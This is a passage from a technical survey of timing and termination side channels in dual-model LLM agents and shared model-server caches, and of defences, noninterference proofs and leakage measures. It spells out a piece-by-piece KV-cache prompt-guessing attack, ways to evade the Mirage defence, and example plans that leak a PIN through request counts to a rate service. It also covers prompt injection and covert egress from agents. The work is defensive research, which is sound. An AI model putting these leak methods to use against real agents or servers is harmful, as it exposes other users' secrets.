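*Governing the KV Cache* (2026) explains why the cache can mix customers. The server divides a prompt into blocks of a fixed number of tokens and gives each block an identifier:

h₀ = H(block 0), and hⱼ = H(hⱼ₋₁, block j).

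H is a hash function, which turns text of any length into a short code. Each identifier depends on the block's own tokens and, through the previous identifier, on everything before it. The formula doesn't include who sent the prompt, so any customer whose prompt begins the same way gets the same identifiers and a cache hit.

Yan and Zhang describe the resulting attack. The attacker is an ordinary customer who knows or can guess how the victim's prompt begins, and he proceeds as follows:

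1. The victim's agent sends a prompt with a known beginning and a secret continuation, and the server caches it.
2. The attacker sends the known beginning followed by one guess at the next piece of the secret.
3. He measures the time until his first token arrives. A fast response suggests that the guess is right.
4. He adds the correct piece to the known beginning and starts guessing the next.

The attack takes few guesses when the attacker can confirm the secret piece by piece. If each digit of a six-digit code is a separate token and the server can match single tokens, he needs at most ten guesses per digit, or 60 in all. If the server matches only whole blocks and all six digits lie in one block, a partly correct guess produces no additional cache hit, so he has to guess the whole code at once, which may take a million attempts. The widely used vLLM matches blocks, while SGLang uses a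 tree of prefixes that allows finer matching.

Noise is a serious obstacle here too, since one more cached token saves very little time. *Characterizing Contention-Induced Reliability Collapse in KV-Cache Timing Side Channels* finds that the signal becomes unreliable when the server is busy. Waiting times and how the server groups requests can change between two identical probes, and cache hits are sometimes even measured as slower than misses.

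*The Early Bird Catches the Leak* (2024) reports that repeating trials a few times made it substantially more accurate to detect single-token cache hits. But a wrong guess also enters the cache, so an attacker who sends it again hits his own earlier probe. He can flood the server with unrelated requests to push out old entries, but this may also remove the victim's prompt, and then he has to wait for the victim to send it again.

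The same work examined commercial services in 2024 and concluded that Claude, DeepSeek and Azure OpenAI used some kind of shared cache, though the providers may have changed their systems since. Some of these caches were semantic. Semantic caches reuse work between prompts with similar meanings, so an attacker can learn the subject of a prompt without guessing its exact words. Research on defences has continued and includes Mirage and the system that Pennas, Papaioannou and colleagues (2026) propose in *CacheSolidarity*.

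In a dual-model agent, the privileged model's prompt would probably be more exposed than the quarantined model's. The quarantined model's prompt might contain fixed instructions, then a question from the plan, then the private text. To guess the private text, an attacker has to know everything before it exactly, and the privileged model may word its question differently each time. "Summarise these letters" and "Summarise the letters" have different keys and values from the second word on. The privileged model's prompt is more predictable because the same instructions and tool descriptions may precede every user's request, so another user of the same product could try to guess the request. The interpreter's labels don't protect either prompt, because the leak occurs on the model server.

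### What researchers have attacked so far

None of these works demonstrates a timing attack on an agent with separate privileged and quarantined models. The two-request leak follows from the way such an agent runs its plan, and its size in practice is unknown. The other attacks may carry over to different degrees:

| What the attacker learns | Where researchers showed it | What may differ in a dual-model agent |
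|---|---|---|
| Topic of a question | 28 model services (McDonald and Bar Or) | Answers to the plan can be short and need no streaming |
| Type or identity of an agent | Agent services (Zhang and colleagues) | The plan is written first, so its tool calls may follow a more regular pattern |
| Category of a shared task | Teams of agents using a small local model (Pouryousef and colleagues) | Quarantined calls add exchanges that depend on private data |
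| Question behind a web search | Research agents running locally (Jeong and colleagues) | The agent still visits sites, but a fixed plan may choose fewer of them |
| Text of another customer's prompt | Model servers with a shared cache (Yan and Zhang) | The attacker has to predict the wording of the plan's questions |

Separating the models may make eavesdropping easier. An ordinary agent mixes planning and reading in each exchange with its model, whereas CaMeL makes a separate request each time the quarantined model has to read something. An eavesdropper who knows the plan, or can guess it from a common task, can match each exchange to a line of the program. The duration and size of that exchange then depend mainly on one piece of private data instead of on everything the agent has done so far.

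## Making elapsed time reveal less

The operator of the exchange-rate service measures the gap between two requests with his own clock, so restricting the plan's clock won't stop him from measuring it. The agent can affect the gap only by changing when it sends the requests.

### Clocks and random delays

*Deterministically Deterring Timing Attacks in Deterland* (Wu and Ford, 2015) describes Deterland, a system for cloud computers that handles inside and outside clocks separately. Programs running on it get a deterministic view of time, and "timing mitigators" pace their output to limit how fast an outsider can learn from its timing. An interpreter could imitate the deterministic clock by advancing the plan's clock one second per line, however long each line takes. The plan that published the duration of a medical summary would then publish the same number every time. The interpreter would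 also have to hide the real time in web servers' replies.

Removing the clock function may not stop an agent from measuring time if it can run arbitrary code. *Hacky Racers* (2022) shows how to build fine-grained timers from ordinary instructions, using the processor's ability to work on several at once. A plan in CaMeL's restricted Python has less control over the processor, but its model calls take seconds, so a much cruder timer would be enough to measure them.

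The agent could wait for a random time before each request to obscure its timing from an outside clock. Suppose a secret changes the average gap between requests by 0.1 seconds and the random delay has a standard deviation of 1 second. A single measurement reveals very little, but the average of 400 measurements has a standard error of 1/√400 = 0.05 seconds, half the difference. An operator who knows the two possible averages can then pick the right one about 84 per cent of the time, or about 98 per cent with 1,600 measurements.

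This noise makes the user wait longer on every run. A delay chosen uniformly at random between 0 and 3.5 seconds has a standard deviation of about 1 second and adds an average of 1.75 seconds to each request. Doubling the range doubles the average delay, and the operator must then average four times as many runs to reduce the noise to the same level.

An attacker may not need to average out random delay. The delay is sometimes close to zero, so the shortest gap he sees approaches the true one as he collects more. If the agent's own work always takes the same time for a given secret, the shortest of 100 gaps gives him the wrong answer less than 3 per cent of the time, compared with 31 per cent for the average of the same gaps. Random delay is therefore most useful for a secret that the agent handles only a few times.

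McDonald and Bar Or tested defences against eavesdropping on streamed answers. Injecting fake packets at random intervals typically doubled or tripled the traffic. It lowered the scores of classifiers that used only timing by about 3 to 8 percentage points for six of eight models, but barely changed them for Gemini 1.5 Flash and Mistral Large. They also simulated sending tokens in groups of five, which removed most of the risk for most of the models tested. For GPT-4o mini, however, the score fell only from 98.2 to 94.8 per cent, and they don't know why.

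### Padding to a fixed time

Instead of adding noise, the interpreter can make every call appear to take equally long:

1. The developer sets a limit for a kind of call, such as 10 seconds.
2. The interpreter starts the call and a timer.
3. If the answer comes early, the interpreter holds it and starts the next line only when the limit is up.
4. If there is no answer by then, the interpreter either keeps waiting or abandons the call.

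If the interpreter keeps waiting after a call exceeds its allotted time, the operator sees the overrun and how long it lasted. If it abandons the call, the user loses the answer, but the next line can still start on time, provided the interpreter returns the failure as a labelled result instead of stopping the run.

Tallam and Miller propose padding sensitive operations to their worst-case running time, as cryptographic libraries do. They also suggest adapting techniques from verified cryptographic software to CaMeL's interpreter. Such software avoids timing leaks by making the instructions it runs independent of the key. But CaMeL's interpreter spends most of its time waiting for a model, often on someone else's server, and rewriting the interpreter would not make the model's answers equally long.

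The worst-case time for a model call is also hard to estimate. At 50 tokens a second, a call that may produce 2,000 tokens of hidden reasoning and a 400-token answer needs a limit of 48 seconds, and it can take longer on a busy server. Ten calls that normally take 3 seconds each would take eight minutes instead of half a minute if each were padded to this limit. A developer could choose a limit that covers 99 per cent of ordinary calls, but an attacker could use an injection to make the model write until it exceeded the limit.

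The interpreter can pad the total time between two outside requests instead of padding each call, because the operator can't see the individual calls in between. This adds less delay, since a slow call can use time left over from a fast one. It also hides how many times a loop ran, as long as the whole loop finishes within the time limit. If each call were padded separately, processing twelve emails would still take twice as long as processing six.

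Holding the model's answer in the interpreter doesn't hide its timing from an eavesdropper between the agent and the model, who sees the answer arrive before the hold begins. Only the model server, or a gateway in front of it, can delay sending the answer.

### Releasing results at set moments

The interpreter can shorten the wait by allowing several possible times to continue. Suppose it continues only at 5, 10, 20, 40 or 80 seconds after a call starts. It then continues at 10 seconds if the call takes 6, and at 40 seconds if the call takes 25. If every call finishes within 80 seconds, the operator can see only five different gaps, so one call reveals at most log₂ 5 bits, or about 2.3. If some calls take longer and the run then stops, there is a sixth outcome and the limit is about 2.6 bits.

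If the operator could distinguish only five gaps instead of thirty, revealing a six-digit code would take nine calls instead of five. Nine calls would still be enough because they allow 5⁹, or about 1.95 million, combinations, and there are only one million possible codes.

The leak keeps adding up because each call starts again with all five possibilities. In *Predictive black-box mitigation of timing channels* (2010), Askarov, Zhang and Myers introduce a general class of software "mitigators" that delay events so that their timing carries only a bounded amount of information. A mitigator predicts when each event will be ready, and releases it at the predicted time. When a prediction fails, it changes the schedule for later events too. In a simplified version with the same five times, the interpreter would work as follows:

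1. It starts by predicting that every call will take 5 seconds.
2. If a call finishes early, the interpreter holds the answer until the predicted time.
3. If a call overruns, the interpreter moves to the next time that is long enough and releases the answer then.
4. It keeps this longer prediction for all later calls.

The predicted time can now only rise, and it can rise at most four times. The operator learns which calls made it rise and by how much. For M calls, the number of sequences he could see is the number of ways to choose four items from M + 4:

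N = (M + 4)(M + 3)(M + 2)(M + 1) / 24.

| Calls | Limit if every call starts again at 5 seconds | Limit if the prediction never falls |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 2.3 bits | 2.3 bits |
| 10 | 23 bits | 10 bits |
| 100 | 232 bits | 22 bits |
| 1,000 | 2,322 bits | 35 bits |

An attacker would now need at least 68 calls to learn the six-digit code. But a single 41-second call makes every later call take 80 seconds. Resetting the schedule would restore the speed but would also let the leak start again. An attacker who can inject text could slow the agent down by making the quarantined model write one very long answer.

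Zhang, Askarov and Myers, in *Predictive Mitigation of Timing Channels for Interactive Systems*, reduce this cost by making separate predictions for different types of request. Their schedule releases the response to request i at

S(i) = max(time request i arrives, time the system is predicted to be free) + p(type of request i),

where p is the predicted duration, which doubles after a misprediction. Each type gets a few tokens and uses one up whenever it overruns. While a type has tokens left, only its own overruns slow it down. Once they run out, overruns by every type count towards its delay. Types with regular timing therefore stay fast when others don't.

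With M requests, R types, l tokens per type and a longest possible duration of T, they limit the leak to

log₂(M + 1) × [(R − 1)(l + 1) + log₂(T + 1) + 1] bits.

They tested the method with a proxy between a browser and real websites, using a page that needed 49 requests. With seven types and five tokens each, the page took about 30 per cent longer to load, and the limit stayed below 850 bits for 100,000 requests. With only two types, the loading time almost tripled. Treating every address as its own type raised the limit to about 4,900 bits and was no faster than using seven.

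Even 850 bits is enough for 42 six-digit codes, although an attacker would need extraordinary control over the delays to use all of them. The limit also depends on a request's type being public. In an agent, the interpreter could use one type for yes-or-no questions and another for summaries, since the plan shows which is which. If it chose the type based on the length of a private letter, that choice would leak information about the length.

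*Language-based control and mitigation of timing channels* (Zhang, Askarov and Myers, 2012) builds the method into a programming language. Programs that pass the language's type checker provably leak only a bounded amount of information through timing that an outside observer can measure, given stated assumptions about the hardware. A similar proof for an agent would also need assumptions about the model server.

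### Changing the order of calls

The cheapest fix for the exchange-rate plan adds no delay at all. The plan can finish its outside calls before it touches the letters:

```
eur = fetch("https://rates.example/EUR")
usd = fetch("https://rates.example/USD")
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise these letters", medical_letters)
save_private_note(summary)
```

The letters now have no effect on the gap between the requests. They can't cause a missing request either, because both requests have gone out before the summary can fail. CaMeL's interpreter could make this change automatically, but FIDES may read a secret before it is clear that another website will be needed.

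Reordering works only when the outside call doesn't need the private result. If the agent has to email the summary to a doctor, it must finish the summary first, so the email's arrival time depends on how long the summary took. Some calls must also stay in order for safety. For example, the agent should check the balance before making a payment. If the agent starts a second task as soon as it finishes the first, the timing of the second task's opening request reveals when the first task ended.

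Combining the two currency requests into one removes the gap between them. Tallam and Miller also suggest batching questions to the quarantined model to save money, such as by putting 100 receipts into one prompt. This replaces 100 durations with one total, but it puts all the receipts in the same input. An injection in one receipt could then make the model's answer depend on the other 99, which separate calls would prevent.

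Another of their proposed cost savings, storing plans for common requests and reusing them without calling the privileged model, could create a timing leak. If several users share this store, and one user's request can add a plan to it, a later user can infer from a fast response that somebody has asked the same thing. Their proposal to replace model calls with ordinary parsers for structured data such as JSON is safer. A parser's running time still depends on its input, but the differences are tiny compared with the seconds a model takes to generate output.

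One recommended defense against timing leaks is to make tool calls in a fixed sequence and at fixed times. An agent might contact the rate service once a minute, sending a dummy request when it has no real request to make. The requests would then not reveal how long the private work took or how much of it there was. However, an urgent request might wait almost a minute, and a bank transfer has no harmless dummy version. A useful dummy must also look genuine to the service that receives it.

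Tallam and Miller describe each of these timing proposals in a few sentences, without experiments. Cock, Ge and colleagues collected 2,000 hours of observations on just two timing channels in the seL4 operating-system kernel and compared several defences on different hardware. Tallam and Miller also cite the wrong paper for CaMeL, one about poisoning language models during training, so their statements about CaMeL need checking against other accounts.

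### Running the plan once for each label

Secure multi-execution separates public requests from private work without anyone having to reorder the plan. *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (Devriese and Piessens, 2010) describes running a program once for each security level. Each run receives real data only up to its own level, with default values in place of anything more secret, and produces only the outputs that belong to its level.

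With two levels, the original exchange-rate plan would run like this:

- The public run receives an empty text instead of the medical letters. It sends both requests to the rate service, but saves no private note.
- The secret run receives the real letters and saves the note. It sends no requests and reuses the replies from the public run.

If the interpreter finishes the public run before starting the secret one, the letters can't affect when the requests leave. Running both at once would be quicker, but they could slow each other down if they shared a model server.

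The technique also closes the leaks through branches and failures. The email to the accountant would come from the public run, which uses a default balance of, say, zero, so the outsider would learn nothing from whether it arrived. The drawback for the user is that the accountant would never get the email and the agent would report no error.

Devriese and Piessens explain in the slides for their talk *Secure Multi-Execution* (2010) that an already secure program keeps its behaviour, because replacing its secrets with default values can't change public outputs that never depended on them.

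A language model complicates this argument because it may return different outputs for the same input. For example, the public run might book one hotel while the secret run writes another hotel's name in the user's notes. To avoid this, the interpreter would have to save the model's outputs from the public run and reuse them in the secret run wherever the input was the same. That would also avoid paying for those outputs twice.

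Calls that involve secrets still cost more. With two levels, the quarantined model summarises both the letters and the empty text. An agent that labels data with sets of permitted readers, as FIDES can, may have many more levels. Three people can form 8 different sets of readers, and ten people can form 1,024. If a plan needed a run for each of the 1,024 sets, and each run made ten model calls with different inputs, the user would pay for 10,240 calls instead of ten. An interpreter could skip any level that the plan's data and outputs never use.

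It could also leave out calls whose results a particular run doesn't need. For the exchange-rate plan, that would remove the empty summary and leave only the two requests in the public run. The overhead would be the same as for the reordered plan.

*Secure multi-execution through static program transformation* (Barthe, Crespo and colleagues, 2012) shows how to get the same protection by rewriting the program in advance, which could suit CaMeL's complete plans. But some tasks need a secret to influence a public action. For example, an agent can't book a table around the user's private appointments if it is given an empty calendar. *Secure Multi-Execution*, by Rafnsson and Sabelfeld, extends the technique to programs that deliberately release selected information. The agent could then give the restaurant one free time, which would reveal that much about the calendar.

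### Defences on the model server

An agent can't use any of these methods to stop another customer from probing a shared model cache. The server's operator could give each customer a separate cache, or get the same effect with a salt, a value unique to the customer that goes into the hash:

h₀ = H(salt, block 0).

Two customers with the same prompt then get different identifiers, and neither can cause a cache hit for the other. In tests by Yan and Zhang, known attacks succeeded at most 1 per cent of the time against either version. But the server has to process common instructions again for each customer. On the largest of three models, this increased the median wait for the first token by about 45 per cent at moderate load. A company that sends all its users' requests through one account would need a separate salt for each user to prevent those users from probing one another.

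Yan and Zhang's Mirage keeps the shared cache and delays answers only when somebody appears to be guessing. An attacker has to try many continuations of the same beginning, so Mirage counts them:

1. The server marks certain prompt beginnings as sensitive.
2. When a user sends a new continuation of one, Mirage adds a point to that user's score. Repeating an old continuation adds nothing, and the score falls by about 0.5 per cent a second.
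3. The first new continuation gets a normal response. A second one soon afterwards takes the score above the limit of 1.
4. Mirage then holds each response until a time that about 97 per cent of cache misses would meet, plus a safety margin. It delays every later token by the same amount, so that they don't arrive in a burst.

The graphics processor does other work while the gateway holds the response. After two quick guesses, the user has to wait about 138 seconds for the score to fall back to the limit.

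Mirage also hides the order of responses. Some servers start with the requests that match the most cached text, so an attacker who sends fifty guesses together can look for which one is answered first. Mirage collects the responses and releases them in random order.

The delay has to increase with the server's load, because a cache miss takes longer when the server is busy. Mirage keeps timing recent misses and fits a line relating their duration to prompt length. Yan and Zhang also tried a method with less overhead, which drew each delay at random from the usual range of miss times. A classifier could still separate hits from misses with a score of 0.67, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. Holding responses until the slow end of the range lowered the score to 0.53 and raised the average added delay from 10 to 35 milliseconds.

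SafeKV, another defence, stops sharing only for prompts that a classifier flags as sensitive. The following results are for Llama-3-8B. The waiting times come from a separate test in which 64 legitimate customers sent prompts beginning with the same sensitive text to a server near full capacity.

| Defence | Success of an attack using response times | Success of an attack using response order | Median wait for the first token |
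|---|---|---|---|
| None | 33.4% | 81.8% | 542 ms |
| Mirage | 0.0% | 0.0% | 611 ms |
| Separate caches | 1.0% | 0.0% | 1,858 ms |
| SafeKV | 0.5% | 0.0% | 1,777 ms |

Mirage added about 1.5 per cent to the wait on ordinary public prompts. A legitimate first request for a sensitive prompt took 150 milliseconds, or 418 milliseconds during an attack. When Mirage kept one score for all users instead of one for each, it misclassified normal sharing as an attack and delayed 93 per cent of legitimate requests in a stress test.

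Yan and Zhang's security proof makes three assumptions. The server must have recognised the beginning as sensitive and already be delaying the responses to all the guesses. The pauses between later tokens must reveal nothing that the first token didn't. And the first-token times for hits and misses must differ by no more than a small amount δ. An attacker who gets N₁ normal responses, each worth at most one bit, then needs at least

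N₁ + (H − N₁) / δ

guesses to recover a secret of H bits with certainty. Yan and Zhang estimate δ at 0.06, so a six-digit code would take at least 317 guesses after allowing for one normal response.

That estimate comes from the smallest model, where the timing signal is weakest, and was calculated by putting the classifier's score into a formula meant for accuracy. On the largest model, a classifier that used the timing of later tokens scored 0.63. For that score, the same calculation gives a δ of 0.26 and a minimum of 74 guesses. A better classifier could raise δ further.

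An attacker could also try to stay below the limit. Each authenticated user has a separate score, so someone with many verified accounts might get one normal response on each. The attacker could instead wait between guesses. This succeeded 76.5 per cent of the time in an idealised test that reset the score before each guess, kept the victim's prompt in the cache throughout and kept the attacker's guesses out of it. Yan and Zhang argue that a real cache would delete the victim's prompt during the wait. This is less certain for an agent that sends the same private instructions every few minutes, because each request can put them back in the cache.

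Mirage doesn't hide how many tokens a model writes, so a longer summary of the medical letters would still delay the agent's second request to the exchange-rate service.

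## What proofs and measurements establish

Most proofs about programs that label data establish termination-insensitive noninterference. In the basic version, a program takes public and secret inputs, runs once and produces a result. If two runs have the same public inputs and both finish, their public results must be the same, even if the secret inputs differ. If either run fails to finish, the definition places no requirement on the pair.

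This plan meets the definition:

```
if balance > 10000: [][0]
post_to_chat("Paperwork done")
```

Every run that finishes makes the same post, but the plan crashes before posting if the balance is high. Anyone who expects the post can therefore infer the high balance from its absence.

Designers accept this leak because a stronger guarantee would rule out too many useful programs. They would have to prove that no secret can make the program hang or crash, or forbid anything that might fail while handling secrets, such as a loop whose length depends on one. This is especially hard for agents, because a quarantined model can return a malformed answer to almost any question about private text. The usual defence of the weaker guarantee is that it lets at most one bit leak per run.

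### Programs that produce output as they run

That defence fails once an observer can see output before the program ends, as Askarov, Hunt and colleagues showed in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (2008). In the form of an agent's plan, their example looks like this:

```
for i in range(10000):
    fetch("https://rates.example/EUR")
    if i == pin: [][0]
```

The requests are identical, and the loop's length is a public constant. The program's position is public at every request, because the only branch that depends on the secret begins and ends on the last line. Tracking the program's position therefore misses this loop, although it catches one that runs `pin` times. If the PIN is 4721, the plan crashes just after its 4,722nd request, and the operator of the rate service can work out the PIN from the number of requests in the log.

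Askarov and colleagues wrote such programs for Jif, FlowCaml and the SPARK Examiner, which check information flow in Java, Caml and Ada, and all three tools accept them. The original example loops forever instead of crashing, but crashing with a stack overflow works just as well.

When a program produces output, the guarantee limits what each output reveals. A new output may shrink the set of secrets consistent with everything the observer has seen, but only by as much as any other output would have at that point. In the PIN example, the 101st request rules out the PINs from 0000 to 0099, and it would rule out the same hundred if it asked for a different currency. If the program has no randomness, every secret therefore produces the same sequence of outputs, though the sequence may stop at a different point for each secret.

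An observer who sees at most t outputs can distinguish at most t + 1 cases. A secret of N bits has 2ᴺ possible values, so a program that always reveals it needs at least 2ᴺ − 1 outputs. If all values are equally likely and the observer guesses after t outputs, the guess is right with probability at most (t + 1)/2ᴺ. For a random four-digit PIN and 100 outputs, the probability is at most 101 in 10,000, or about 1 per cent.

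These limits protect long random secrets very well but barely protect short ones. In a test with FlowCaml on a 3 GHz computer, Askarov and colleagues leaked a 32-bit number in under six seconds. Their program wrote to shared memory, which is much faster than printing, and a second program detected when the writes stopped. At that speed, leaking a credit card number of about 50 bits would take about 18½ days, and leaking a 128-bit encryption key would be infeasible. An agent's web requests are far slower, but at ten requests a second the loop above can still find any four-digit PIN in less than 17 minutes. It can identify a diagnosis from a list of ten conditions in at most ten requests.

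### Programs that an attacker can run again

Repeated runs can leak long secrets much faster. In *Multi-run security* (2011), Birgisson and Sabelfeld consider programs that produce no output until they finish, but that an attacker can run again with a different public input. One of their examples hangs if the secret and the attacker's number have a binary 1 in the same position. The attacker sends 1, 2, 4, 8 and so on, testing one binary digit of the secret per run. They used a short Python script to run this attack on a program that Jif had certified, and extracted about one bit per second, at which rate a credit card number would take less than a minute.

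The difference from 18½ days arises because each new run here can rule out half of the remaining values, whereas a counting loop rules out one at a time. Birgisson and Sabelfeld mention a real attack of this kind on ASP.NET, Microsoft's software for websites, in which the attacker compared the error messages from many requests.

Their remedy is to let a loop condition depend on secrets or on data the attacker controls, but not on both. If it depends only on secrets, the program hangs or finishes the same way every time, so the attacker learns nothing from a second run. He also learns nothing when the condition depends only on his own input. They prove that a program that follows this rule and the usual rules for secret branches leaks at most one bit about an unchanging secret, however often the attacker runs it.

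A dual-model agent easily breaks the rule that visible behaviour must not depend on private data. When the quarantined model reads an attacker's email together with a private code, its answer depends on both, so the plan must never fail because of that answer. Returning errors as labelled values would help, provided nothing visible later depends on them.

The proof concerns one fixed program, so it does not cover CaMeL's retry loop, which brings in a new plan after each failure. It also does not cover plans that make visible calls while running. Birgisson and Sabelfeld studied such programs and found the one-bit limit hard to keep, because any visible effect after a step that might hang reveals that the step finished.

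### Runs that depend on a language model

Because a language model's answers are partly random, Garby and colleagues compare the probabilities of different outcomes. Their language assigns a probability to each final state a program can reach. These probabilities form a subdistribution, meaning that they may add up to less than one. The missing part is the probability that the run never reaches a final state, because it loops forever or the interpreter stops it.

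Suppose an agent chooses between two equally good hotels, and a secret in the user's calendar affects only which runs the interpreter stops:

| Outcome | Probability with secret A | Probability with secret B |
|---|---|---|
| Books hotel X | 0.50 | 0.40 |
| Books hotel Y | 0.48 | 0.50 |
| Run stops (the missing part) | 0.02 | 0.10 |

Without any stops, the agent would book hotel X in half its runs and hotel Y in the other half. When the secret is A, the interpreter stops two runs in a hundred, both of which would have booked Y. When the secret is B, it stops ten in a hundred, all of which would have booked X.

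Ordinary noninterference would require the two columns to be equal, but the weaker property of Garby and colleagues requires only that they be compatible. Two columns are compatible if, after final states that look the same to the observer are grouped together, some third list of probabilities is at least as large as both columns for every finished outcome and adds up to no more than one. Here, a list with 0.50 for each hotel meets both conditions. If secret B instead led to X with probability 0.60 and Y with 0.30, the third list would need at least 0.60 for X and 0.48 for Y, which add up to 1.08. Unfinished runs could not explain that difference, so the secret must have affected the choice of hotel.

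Garby and colleagues first tried a simpler definition that compared only finished runs, and found that it was wrong. The hotel example suggests why, since 51 per cent of finished runs book hotel X with secret A and 44 per cent with secret B, even though the secret's only effect is to stop some runs from finishing.

Their main theorem states that every program in the language has the compatibility property, including programs that request code from a model and then run it. To prove it, they define a second way of running programs, in which the interpreter skips any part of the work once its label becomes secret and substitutes an empty value. Since these runs never use the secret, their probabilities are the same for A and B. They also reach each visible outcome at least as often as the real runs, because a skipped step cannot stop the run. The skipping runs therefore supply the third list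 that compatibility requires.

Garby and colleagues apply the property to a newer setting, but acknowledge that Smith and Alpízar had already proposed essentially the same condition for a small language with coin flips. Smith and Alpízar's proof removed the secret parts of a program before running it, which is impossible if a model writes some of the code during the run.

### What the leakage bound says

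Compatibility also limits how far apart two lists of outcomes can be. Write μ(q) and ν(q) for the probabilities of a finished outcome q with the two secrets, and define their distance as

Δ = ½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)|.

The theorem implies that the distance Δ is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. If those probabilities are 0.02 and 0.10, Δ is at most 0.06.

The reason is short. The gap between any two numbers is twice the larger one minus their sum. Compatibility means that the larger probabilities, added over all finished outcomes, come to at most 1. The finished outcomes alone add up to 0.98 with secret A and 0.90 with secret B, so

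Δ ≤ 1 − ½(0.98 + 0.90) = 0.06.

The hotel example reaches this limit, since ½(0.10 + 0.02) = 0.06. If every run finished, the limit would be zero, so the two columns would be equal.

However, 0.06 is too low for an observer who notices failures, because it covers only finished runs and the failure rates differ by 0.08. If a stopped run counts as a third outcome, the distance in the example is ½(0.10 + 0.02 + 0.08) = 0.10. An observer who thinks A and B equally likely can then guess the secret correctly 55 per cent of the time from one run. With failures included, the same argument limits the distance in general to the larger of the two failure probabilities.

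An observer who only counts failures guesses the secret correctly 54 per cent of the time after one run, about 90 per cent after 50 and about 96 per cent after 100. These figures assume that the observer knows both failure rates, the secret stays the same and the runs are independent.

This does not contradict the theorem. If the 50 requests form a single program that ends at the first stop, the probability that it fails to finish is 0.64 for secret A and 0.995 for secret B. The limit on the distance then rises to about 0.82, which gives almost no protection. If a user or an outside retry loop starts the 50 runs separately, the theorem covers each run but not the series.

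### Attacker-chosen text and machine-checked proofs

A second theorem by Garby and colleagues covers secrecy when an attacker chooses all the untrusted inputs the agent reads. Whatever text the attacker supplies, changing a secret cannot change the public results except by stopping runs. This remains true if the plan endorses some of the attacker's text as trusted.

The theorem depends on how the developer divides a label into a trust part, which endorsement can change, and a secrecy part, which it cannot. If the whole label were in the trust part, endorsement could remove any restriction, and the theorem would guarantee nothing. The developer also has to label the data sources correctly and place a check in front of every sensitive tool. Under those conditions, the theorem guarantees that a plan without endorsement complies with the policy, even if the attacker controls the model that wrote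 it.

The proof assistant Lean has checked each step of the proofs of these theorems. The interpreter that runs the agent is itself a Lean program, and a third theorem connects it to the mathematics. This theorem treats the model as a table that lists an answer for every possible conversation at every call. Filling in the table at random according to the model's probabilities and then running the interpreter produces each outcome with exactly the probability that the theory predicts. This closes a common gap in such work between the system in the proof and the program that people run. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL has no comparable theorem, and its designers call formal proof a "crucial direction" for further work.

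Lean does not verify the code that sends requests to the real model, and the third theorem assumes that the model's answers follow fixed probabilities for a given conversation. The secrecy theorems assume nothing about how the interpreter parses an answer, so strange output from an attacker-controlled model does not weaken them.

### What the proofs leave out

The formal model does not include elapsed time. An observer sees only the final state, which consists of a conversation and a value, so two runs that end in the same state count as the same even if one takes a second and the other a minute. The interpreter counts its steps to stop runaway programs, but the theorem about it concerns only whether some number of steps is enough. The formal model also has no observer who can watch the network or share a model server with the agent, because it represents a call to the language model only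 as a random draw.

The banking tools in RANDORI are also part of the program, written as functions that take one state of a simulated world and return another. Garby and colleagues list this as a limitation. It matters most when a run stops halfway. In the model, such a run has no final state, so the comparison leaves out both the run and any emails it sent, although in a real system those emails would still have been sent.

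The PIN-counting plan falls into this gap. Its last step crashes whatever the PIN is, so the plan never reaches a final state and there is nothing to compare under the theorem. If `fetch` contacted a real server, the server's operator would have received thousands of requests before the crash. Askarov and colleagues' definition for output would describe this leak, but their theory covers only programs without randomness. A guarantee for agents with real tools would have to account for both output and randomness.

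The reasoning-integrity theorem of Jiang and colleagues similarly excludes delays that an outsider measures. It also compares only runs that follow the same schedule up to the same point, so it assumes that untrusted data does not change the schedule. The theorem concerns what untrusted data can influence, so it does not establish where secrets can go.

Leaks outside the tracked part of a system occur in practice. In 2026, the security company Check Point reported two flaws in the containers, or closed-off environments, where ChatGPT runs code. One flaw involved DNS queries, which turn a website's name into a network address. A program can leak data by including it in the name being looked up. The other flaw involved shared metadata about software packages. Neither case concerned a dual-model agent, but an interpreter that checks only tool calls could not stop either kind of leak.

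### Four ways to measure a leak

Where a proof allows some leakage or does not apply, the remaining option is to measure the leakage. The usual measures capture different things and can give very different results for the same system.

Mutual information is the average number of bits that an observation Y gives about a secret X:

I(X;Y) = Σ p(x,y) log₂ [ p(x,y) / (p(x) p(y)) ].

The mutual information between the secret and the observation is zero exactly when they are independent. If the two calendar secrets in the hotel example are equally likely, one run reveals about 0.025 bits.

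Channel capacity is the largest mutual information a sender could achieve by choosing how often to send each signal. It suits covert channels, where the sender tries to send as much as possible. Engineers often divide it by the time per signal to get bits per second.

Min-entropy leakage measures how much an observation helps someone guess a secret in one try. Birgisson and Sabelfeld take this measure from Smith, who measures uncertainty as −log₂ V, where V is the probability that the best guess is right. The leakage is the uncertainty before the observation minus the uncertainty after it. In the hotel example, the observation raises V from 0.50 to 0.55, so the leakage is about 0.14 bits. If a program has no randomness and all values of the secret are equally likely, the leakage is log₂ of the number of possible outputs.

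Whether leakage is measured as an average or by the success of a single guess matters most for rare, severe leaks. Suppose one run in a hundred reveals an entire six-digit code and the others reveal nothing. The mutual information, which averages over all runs, is only 0.2 bits. But a thief's chance of guessing the code in one try rises from one in a million to one in a hundred, which is a min-entropy leakage of 13.3 bits.

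A statistical test on observed traces needs no model of the channel. The tester records what an observer would see, such as the times and sizes of messages, over many runs with each of two secrets. The tester then checks whether the two sets of traces differ by more than chance, or whether a trained classifier can tell them apart. McDonald and Bar Or used classifiers this way on encrypted traffic in *Whisper Leak*.

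A test that finds no leak may have been too small to detect one. With the earlier failure rates of 2 and 10 per cent, a tester who does 50 runs with each secret would typically see one failure with one secret and five with the other. If he shuffled the 100 results at random between the two secrets, he would get a gap at least that large about a fifth of the time, so he could not call it a leak. With 200 runs for each secret, he would typically see 4 failures and 20, and only about one shuffle in a thousand would produce a gap that large. An attacker who already knows the two rates needs fewer runs than the tester, because 50 in all are enough to identify the secret correctly 90 per cent of the time.

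### Measuring a monitor for outgoing messages

Metere (2026), in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, applied mutual information to the messages that agents send (egress). The monitor is designed for an attacker who already controls what the agent tries to send and when. It passes each text through ten stages, including ones that remove invisible characters, put data fields in a standard order, and replace synonyms with one standard word. It can also delay or cancel a message, and it limits how much suspicious data each destination can receive over time.

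To test the monitor, Metere built fifteen working encoders for text, images and audio, each with a matching decoder. In every trial, a program draws random secret bits, hides them in a harmless message, sends the message through the monitor and tries to read the bits from the output.

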